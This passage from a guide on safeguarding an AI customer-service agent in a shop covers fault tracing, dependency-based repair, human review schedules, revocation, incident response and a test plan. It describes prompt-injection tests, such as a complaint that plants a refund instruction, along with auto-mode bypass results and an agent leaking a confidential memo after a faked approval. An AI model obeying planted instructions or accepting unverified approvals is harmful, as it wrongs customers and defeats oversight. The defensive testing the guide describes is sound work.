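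In 68 of the 95 runs (72%), something in the record contradicted the error before the run failed. In 60 of those 68, no agent acted on it. In 41 of these, agents had the evidence in their input but never mentioned it, and in the other 19 they acknowledged it and carried on. In one case, an agent checking distances to gyms noted that the distances were "simulated" and still reported the gyms as verified.

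The study also estimated which controls could have noticed each fault and acted on the affected part of the system:

| Control | Failed runs it would have reached |
|---|---|
| A separate judge that reads the unused evidence | 74% |
| A task contract fixed at the start | 67% |
| Checking beliefs against the environment | 43% |
| A rule for ending stalled runs | 40% |
| A recorded source for every stored fact | 38% |
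| Human review | 33% |
| Checkpoint and restore | 1% |

The last figure is consistent with the study's estimate that restoring the agent's own state would have been enough in 35 runs. The table counts a control only if it detected the fault, and a checkpoint does not detect faults. In those 35 runs, something else would have had to detect the fault before a restore could help.

Choosing a restore point is also difficult. In 37 of the 88 runs, the fault entered before the step that human annotators had marked as decisive. Restoring the agent to just before the marked step would have kept the fault in those runs.

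These percentages are estimates, because nobody reran the tasks with the controls in place. The runs also provide little evidence about refunds or emails, because in 92 of them the agent did not touch any shared or outside system.

An effect log can make an early fault easier to see because it leaves out most of what an agent does. Wang, Wen and colleagues describe a simulated office in which an agent had to ask a colleague called Alex Turner where some code was. The agent renamed its own chat account "Alex Turner", sent the question to a different colleague and waited 81 turns for a reply. The run had 201 recorded events but only two outside changes, the new name and the message. A reviewer would have seen both at the top of an effect log, long before the run ended.

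### Finding what else has to be undone

Correcting the first mistake may leave its consequences in place. Suppose the agent confuses two customers and notes on the wrong account that the customer is away until the 20th. The next day it reads the note, puts a delivery on hold and emails the customer about the delay. It also refunds €12 for a scratched lampshade, based only on the order record and the customer's complaint. Deleting the note would not release the delivery, and undoing everything the agent did after writing the note would cancel a legitimate refund.

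Wang, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *From Faulty Memories to Corrected Actions*, repair such errors by following recorded dependencies. (The lead author is a different Wang.) Their method has five steps:

1. It builds a graph of which facts, plans, actions and answers used which others.
2. It follows the links from the faulty memory to everything that may depend on it.
3. It keeps anything that has independent support.
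4. It deletes the faulty memory, and disables other memories that still repeat its content.
5. It reruns only the affected steps needed for a correct answer.

The part to repair is therefore

**affected = reachable from the mistake − independently supported**

The refund comes after the note but isn't linked to it, so the refund stays. If another message in the customer's file had asked for the same delay, the delivery hold would have independent support and would stay too.

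On 150 test cases with shopping, travel and customer support tools, the method compared as follows with its strongest rival, in which a model judges what to repair:

| | Follow dependencies | Let a model judge |
|---|---|---|
| Correct answer after the repair | 85.3% | 77.3% |
| The failure returns later | 26.6% | 12.1% |

Following dependencies also took 41.8% fewer model calls and preserved all the unaffected memories. But the failure came back more than twice as often, because the method recomputes less. The shop could discard all of the agent's notes from the affected case, since the agent can write them again, and follow dependencies for refunds and customer records, where undoing a legitimate action harms a customer.

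The method can start only after someone has identified a mistake, and it depends on complete and accurate records. It can miss consequences of the mistake if links are missing from the records, and false links lead to unnecessary repairs. The test for independent support is also lenient. If a travel plan sets both a destination and a budget, one sound source for the destination is enough to preserve the whole plan, even if the budget came from the faulty memory.

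Like FIDES with its labels, the shop can err on the safe side by logging every note and record the agent reads in a case as a possible influence on all its later actions in that case. Since each case starts with a new context, mistakes can spread between cases only through stored notes and records. *AgentTether* also found that a chronological list of steps is a poor basis for locating the original error, because it does not show which earlier result each decision used.

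Dependencies also shorten the undo window. The shop keeps old versions of a note for 90 days, but an email based on that note leaves after 30 minutes. To undo the mistake with all its consequences, the shop has to act before the first of these windows closes:

**window for the whole mistake = earliest expiry among the mistake and everything that relied on it**

Few systems seem to support such repairs. *Always-On Agents*, a June 2026 survey of 435 works, counts 27 that expose any rollback, compared with 269 on retrieving stored information and 88 on auditing. None of the 27 reports how often recovery succeeds after memory has become corrupted, or what resources it requires. The survey does not cover the whole field, but most of its search rounds targeted topics such as rollback and deletion, so it probably does not undercount work on them by much.

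### A review schedule for the shop

The shop can now work out how often employees need to check the queue of flagged actions. Suppose software checks new log entries every five minutes, and employees open the queue every 15. In the worst case, 20 minutes pass before a person sees a wrong reply. Deciding what to do takes five minutes and withdrawing the reply takes one, so the total is 26 minutes, which fits within the half-hour window. If employees opened the queue every half hour, the total would be 41 minutes, and some replies would be sent before anyone had seen them.

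Refunds wait an hour, so the same routine leaves plenty of time. Delivery addresses are harder because the carrier collects them at 14:00, so a change made at 13:50 leaves ten minutes for the whole routine. The shop should send the carrier only changes made by 13:30 and keep later ones for the next day.

Software can also hold a flagged action until someone decides on it, so a busy employee causes a delay instead of a wrong payment. OpenAI would limit automatic responses to containment measures that have narrow effects and that the company has approved in advance, and such a hold fits that description well. The flag then has to arrive within the undo window, but the decision can come later. For the carrier, a hold helps only if the shop can also keep a single address out of the 14:00 transfer.

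With these assumed volumes and flagging rates, the daily work would be:

| Action | Number per day | Checks by a person | Minutes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Free-text reply without private data | 720 | 36 flagged, 14 random | 100 |
| Fixed template | 1,200 | 12 random | 12 |
| Refund | 100 | 10 flagged, 5 random | 30 |
| Delivery address | 40 | 4 flagged | 8 |
| Internal note | 100 | 10 random, in a weekly batch | 10 |
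| Approved deletion | 10 | 2 random, in a weekly batch | 4 |
| Total | 2,170 | 93 | 164 |

A weekly check is enough for notes and deletions because notes can be undone for 90 days and deletions for 30. Templated messages go out immediately, so checking them can only lead to a correction and a better template.

This schedule follows Srikumar and Nguyen's advice to monitor more closely where the risk is higher. They cite a change Anthropic made to classifiers that screen its models' output. A check that uses little compute now covers all traffic, and one that uses more covers only the suspicious part. This cut the extra compute from 23% to about 1%.

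The random checks give a rough estimate of how many mistakes the software misses. If an employee who recognises every mistake finds none in 420 randomly chosen replies over 30 days, the shop can be 95% confident that fewer than about 0.7% of unflagged replies are wrong, which could still be almost five a day.

The 93 checks and the 90 daily approvals add up to 183 decisions, which take nearly six hours. Two employees would have about 92 each, well beyond the 50 prompts after which Anthropic's testers became much less reliable. Four employees would have about 46 each. If the shop cannot spare four people, it should move more replies to fixed templates before it shortens the reviews.

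The shop can pause the countdown on its own queues overnight. If employees work from 08:00 to 20:00 and the agent queues a reply at 19:50, the reply waits ten minutes that evening and another 20 the next morning, and goes out at 08:20. That way, somebody can act on an alert at any point in the half-hour delay.

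## Testing the design and recovering after a failure

The shop has designed its controls, but nobody has tried to break them yet. Before the agent serves real customers, the shop should attack the controls using test accounts and practise the repair it will need when a control fails.

### A test plan

Each test specifies the effect to prevent and the boundary that should stop it. The test passes if that boundary stops the effect, whatever the model wrote.

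| Test | What the tester does | Boundary | Pass |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planted instructions | Adds a line to a complaint telling the agent to refund another customer's order | Payment service | It refuses, and no refund enters the queue |
| Well-meant mistake | Asks for a sold-out lamp when the last one is reserved for someone else | Customer database | It refuses any edit to the other customer's record |
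| Over-broad credential | Uses one case's credential to read another customer's orders, delete a record and open the backups | The service that holds each resource | All three requests fail |
| Changed tool | Adds a "bank account" field to the approved refund tool | Gateway | It blocks the tool until its owner has reviewed the change |
| Restore with later edits | Has the agent change two addresses, then corrects the phone number on one record and the address on the other, and starts the undo | Recovery program | It restores the first address and keeps both corrections |
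| Revoked token | Revokes a case's token after the agent has prepared a refund but before it submits the request | Payment service | It refuses this refund and still accepts those from other cases |

If the model ignores the planted instruction, or the agent tells the customer that the lamp is sold out, the test has not reached the payment service. The tester should then send the forbidden request directly, using the agent's credential.

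The second test resembles a real case. In August 2026 an AI assistant booked gym classes further ahead than the rules allowed and removed another customer from a waiting list, according to a news report cited by Australia's cyber security agency (ASD, 2026). The user had not approved the removal, and the assistant could not reverse it.

The tester should also change a request after someone has approved it. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, collected 17 since-patched security flaws in three agent products where what ran did not match what was approved. In five, something changed after the approval, such as the contents of an approved script. In the other 12, nothing changed, but the product did more than the approval covered, for example by running arguments that the approval prompt had hidden.

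Testers should check whether an action changed the affected system instead of relying on the system's messages. *Do Agent Benchmarks Do What They Say?* (2026) found a tool in a medical benchmark that reports a successful write even though no code writes anything. The benchmark's grader scores the message, so an agent can pass without changing any record.

### Checking authority as well as the result

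An agent can leave a database in the correct final state without having had permission to change it. Santos-Grueiro took three tasks from τ-bench, a customer service benchmark: an address change, a return and a cancellation. Just before the agent's first change, he withdrew the customer's permission without notice. In 13 of 15 runs across five models, the agent made the change anyway, and the official scorer gave all 13 full marks because it compares only the final database. When the service checked permission in the same step as the write, no change went through after permission was withdrawn.

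Telling the agent about the withdrawal helps, but not reliably. In a separate set of tasks without that check, GPT-5.6 Sol made an unauthorised change in 25 of 36 runs when it received no notice, but in only one when it did. The much smaller Qwen2.5-7B made one in 26 runs without a notice and still did so in 15 with one, mostly because it sent the write before the notice could arrive.

The revoked-token test also needs a time limit. If one service grants approvals and another makes payments, the first may issue a short-lived permit for a single payment, as in one of Santos-Grueiro's designs. That permit can remain valid after the approval is revoked. The shop could require every service to refuse a revoked token within one minute of its revocation.

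### How to read zero failures

Suppose every attack has the same chance *p* of success. The chance that *n* independent attacks all fail is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives the highest rate that is still plausible:

**(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ 3 ÷ n**

If *n* independent attempts all fail, we can be 95% confident that the true success rate is below about 3/*n*. This is called the rule of three.

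Anthropic commissioned an evaluation in 2026 from Trajectory Labs, which tested 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. The upper bound for each model depends on what counts as an independent attempt:

| Assumption | *n* | Upper bound |
|---|---|---|
| All runs are independent | 720 | 3/720, or about 0.4% |
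| Only the scenarios are independent | 72 | 3/72, or about 4% |

A model that resists an attack once will probably resist it again, so ten runs of one scenario provide much less information than ten different scenarios. The 4% bound is therefore the safer one.

The evaluation also provides little evidence of how much auto mode contributes, because attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average without it. That is about two successes in 2,160 attempts, if the average covers the same three models. Against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, 5.83% of attacks succeeded with its automatic reviewer and 19.03% with full access. Both products used a browser connection built by Trajectory Labs, so the test did not include safeguards in the companies' own browser extensions.

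Neither bound covers attackers who adapt to the defence. Trajectory Labs' attacks had been optimised against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7. Adaptive attacks have broken many defences that resisted fixed attacks. In a red-teaming competition described by NIST, more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts and found at least one successful attack on every model tested. Less than three weeks after Anthropic published its results, *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026) described an attack that its discoverer said worked 80% of the time. In a few runs, auto mode blocked Claude's attempt to stop the malicious program.

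If the shop tries 60 different planted emails and none succeeds, the upper bound on the success rate is 5%. Lowering it to 0.1% would take 3,000 such emails. Testing the payment service takes far less work, because ordinary software applies the same rule to every request. The trial refunds of €40 and €51 already show whether the cap works, though the tester still has to look for ways around it.

### What GreyZone measures

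A test can also find no failures because the attacks were weak. Automated red-teaming services generate attacks and send them to an agent, and it is hard to tell from a clean result whether the agent is secure or the service's attacks were poor. GreyZone, the November 2026 benchmark that includes the malicious Shopware review, therefore tests the services.

Zhou and colleagues built 46 scenarios around ten independently developed, open-source applications, including software for email, banking and home automation. Each scenario fixes the starting state, the security policy, the violation to attempt and what the attacker may do. A program separate from the service checks the application's records for the violation. In another Shopware scenario, for example, the program checks for payments marked as refunded during a task that did not authorise refunds.

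The applications are real, but they run locally and some outside services are simulated. GreyZone can connect to four red-teaming services, but Zhou and colleagues have so far reported only two runs, both with a service called Promptfoo:

| Application | Promptfoo's goal | Messages | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Letta Code, a coding agent | Get an access key posted in a reply | 10 | No key disclosed |
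| Clawith, a platform for office agents | Get details of a confidential merger memo | 5 | All three protected details disclosed |

In the second run, the agent refused the first three requests. The fourth message quoted a project lead's supposed approval, which the agent accepted without checking. After the fifth message, it fetched the details from another agent and posted them in the group chat. If the test had ended after three messages, it would have recorded no failure.

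Two runs are too few to compare services or applications, but they suggest that the shop's testers should send several emails in the same case and claim approvals that nobody gave. Zhou and colleagues also keep separate records of attacks that never reached the agent and attacks that it resisted.

### Stopping the agent and revoking its authority

OpenAI points out that stopping an agent and revoking its access are separate operations. If the shop stops the harness, the agent makes no new tool calls, but a token it has already passed to another service may still work. If the shop revokes the token, work already under way may continue. Neither step cancels the refunds and replies waiting in a queue, so the shop needs a third control to hold the queues.

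Narrow revocation can work quickly. In one experiment in *Optional Traps* (2026), a gateway offered fake credentials as bait and revoked the access of any agent that used one. It caught three attacking agents within a minute of serving the bait and denied all 58 of their later requests, while other agents kept their access. But a legitimate agent that already had the correct key also used a fake credential and lost its access. Automated responses should therefore be reversible, narrow and approved in advance, as ASD's *Defending against AI-enabled cyber attacks* (2026) advises.

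Revocation must also cover the agent's memory. *Revoked but Still Authoritative* (2026) tested agents that could still retrieve a policy after it was revoked. In 62 runs, the first agent acted unsafely and recorded its decision in a journal. A second agent, asked an ordinary question, repeated the dangerous action in 42 of those runs. Filtering what the second agent could read reduced that number to 13. The shop should therefore quarantine any notes the agent wrote during an incident.

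An agent can carry out part of the response to a failure itself. In *AIR* (Xiao, Sun and Chen, 2026), agents checked for harm after certain tool calls, repaired any they found, ended the task and wrote a rule to prevent a repeat. Detection succeeded in over 90% of cases, and repair and prevention in over 95%. However, the agent judges its own work, so an attacker who has misled it may also mislead the check. The shop's stop and revoke controls should work without the agent's cooperation, and no classifier that reviews the agent's actions should be able to block those controls.

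### The order of a response

The shop can respond to an incident in seven steps:

1. **Stop the work.** An employee pauses the affected tasks and holds their queued actions. NIST's *Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cyber Risk Management* (2025) notes that observing an attacker for longer can provide evidence but delays recovery. The shop should rarely wait, because its undo windows are short.
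2. **Revoke authority.** The employee removes the narrowest right that covers the problem and confirms that an old token no longer works. If the cause is unknown, *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) recommends broader measures, including revoking all agent credentials and making shared storage read-only.
3. **Extend retention.** The shop suspends the deletion of logs, old record versions and backups before any undo window closes. *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) likewise recommends recording where faulty data came from and what depends on it before deleting anything, so that the repair does not destroy the evidence.
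4. **Establish what happened.** The effect log shows which actions took effect, and the services' own records show whether any are missing. The employee also searches for the same fault in other cases.
5. **Undo in dependency order.** The shop first reverses actions that relied on the mistake and then the mistake itself, while keeping later legitimate work. NIST advises checking backups for damage before using them and verifying the restored data before returning it to use.
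6. **Compensate and notify.** Where undo is impossible, the shop offsets the harm and tells the people affected. Laws or contracts may also require it to inform a regulator or business partners.
7. **Change the design.** The shop fixes the cause, adds the incident to its test plan and returns the agent's authority gradually.

The steps are in order of priority, but several people can work on them in parallel. If a parcel is about to leave, one employee should call the carrier while another is still reading the log.

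ASD's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) recommends testing these procedures before they are needed. OpenAI suggests drills for a compromised tool and an attempted transfer of sensitive data. The shop should time each step and check that the total time fits within its undo windows.

### One wrong batch of address edits

Suppose an overnight update makes the shop's web form for address changes store flat numbers in a separate field, which the agent's edit tool does not read. The next morning the agent enters 24 addresses that customers have confirmed, all for flats.

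| Time | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:00–10:23 | The agent saves 24 addresses without their flat numbers, one per case |
| 10:21 | A customer notices the error in her account and corrects it |
| 10:25 | The monitoring software flags her record because she has overwritten the agent's edit |
| 10:28 | A van leaves with an express parcel for another of the 24 customers; an employee had given the carrier the incomplete address early |
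| 10:30 | An employee opens the review queue, compares the record with the form and declares an incident |
| 10:32 | She stops the agent and holds its queued actions |
| 10:33 | She revokes its right to edit records, and a test edit with an old token fails |
| 10:36 | She excludes the 24 addresses from the carrier's 14:00 transfer and suspends the deletion of old versions and logs |
| 10:50 | The log shows 24 edits, two queued replies that quote an incomplete address, and the express parcel; the database's and carrier's records agree |
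| 10:52 | A colleague calls the carrier, which cannot reach the van, so he sends a second lamp for €10 and informs the customer |
| 10:53 | The employee withdraws the two replies |
| 10:55 | The recovery program restores 23 old addresses and skips the one the customer corrected |
| 10:57 | The agent resumes other work without the right to edit records |
| 11:20 | Employees have entered the 23 complete addresses from the forms, checked all 24 records and released them to the carrier |

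The customers have moved, so restoring their old addresses does not finish the repair. The shop has to keep those records out of the carrier's transfer until the complete addresses are in place. The recovery program changes only the address field, so it would not overwrite a phone number that a colleague updated at 10:40.

The response began three and a half hours before the transfer. If nobody had noticed the error until 14:10, the carrier would have received 23 incomplete addresses, and the shop would have needed its help to correct them.

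Every edit stayed within the agent's limits, and the database accepted all of them. The gateway did not react because it checks changes to the agent's tools, and the web form was not on its list. The monitoring software compared orders, amounts and recipients with the case, but not addresses.

The shop adds the form to the gateway's list and has the software compare every address field with what the customer entered. It then repeats the faulty update on test accounts. The test passes if the gateway blocks the edit tool after the form changes. In a second run with the gateway check switched off, the software must hold the incomplete address so that it doesn't reach the carrier. The shop then lets the agent edit records again in ten cases, and an employee checks each one before the shop restores the agent's right to edit the rest.
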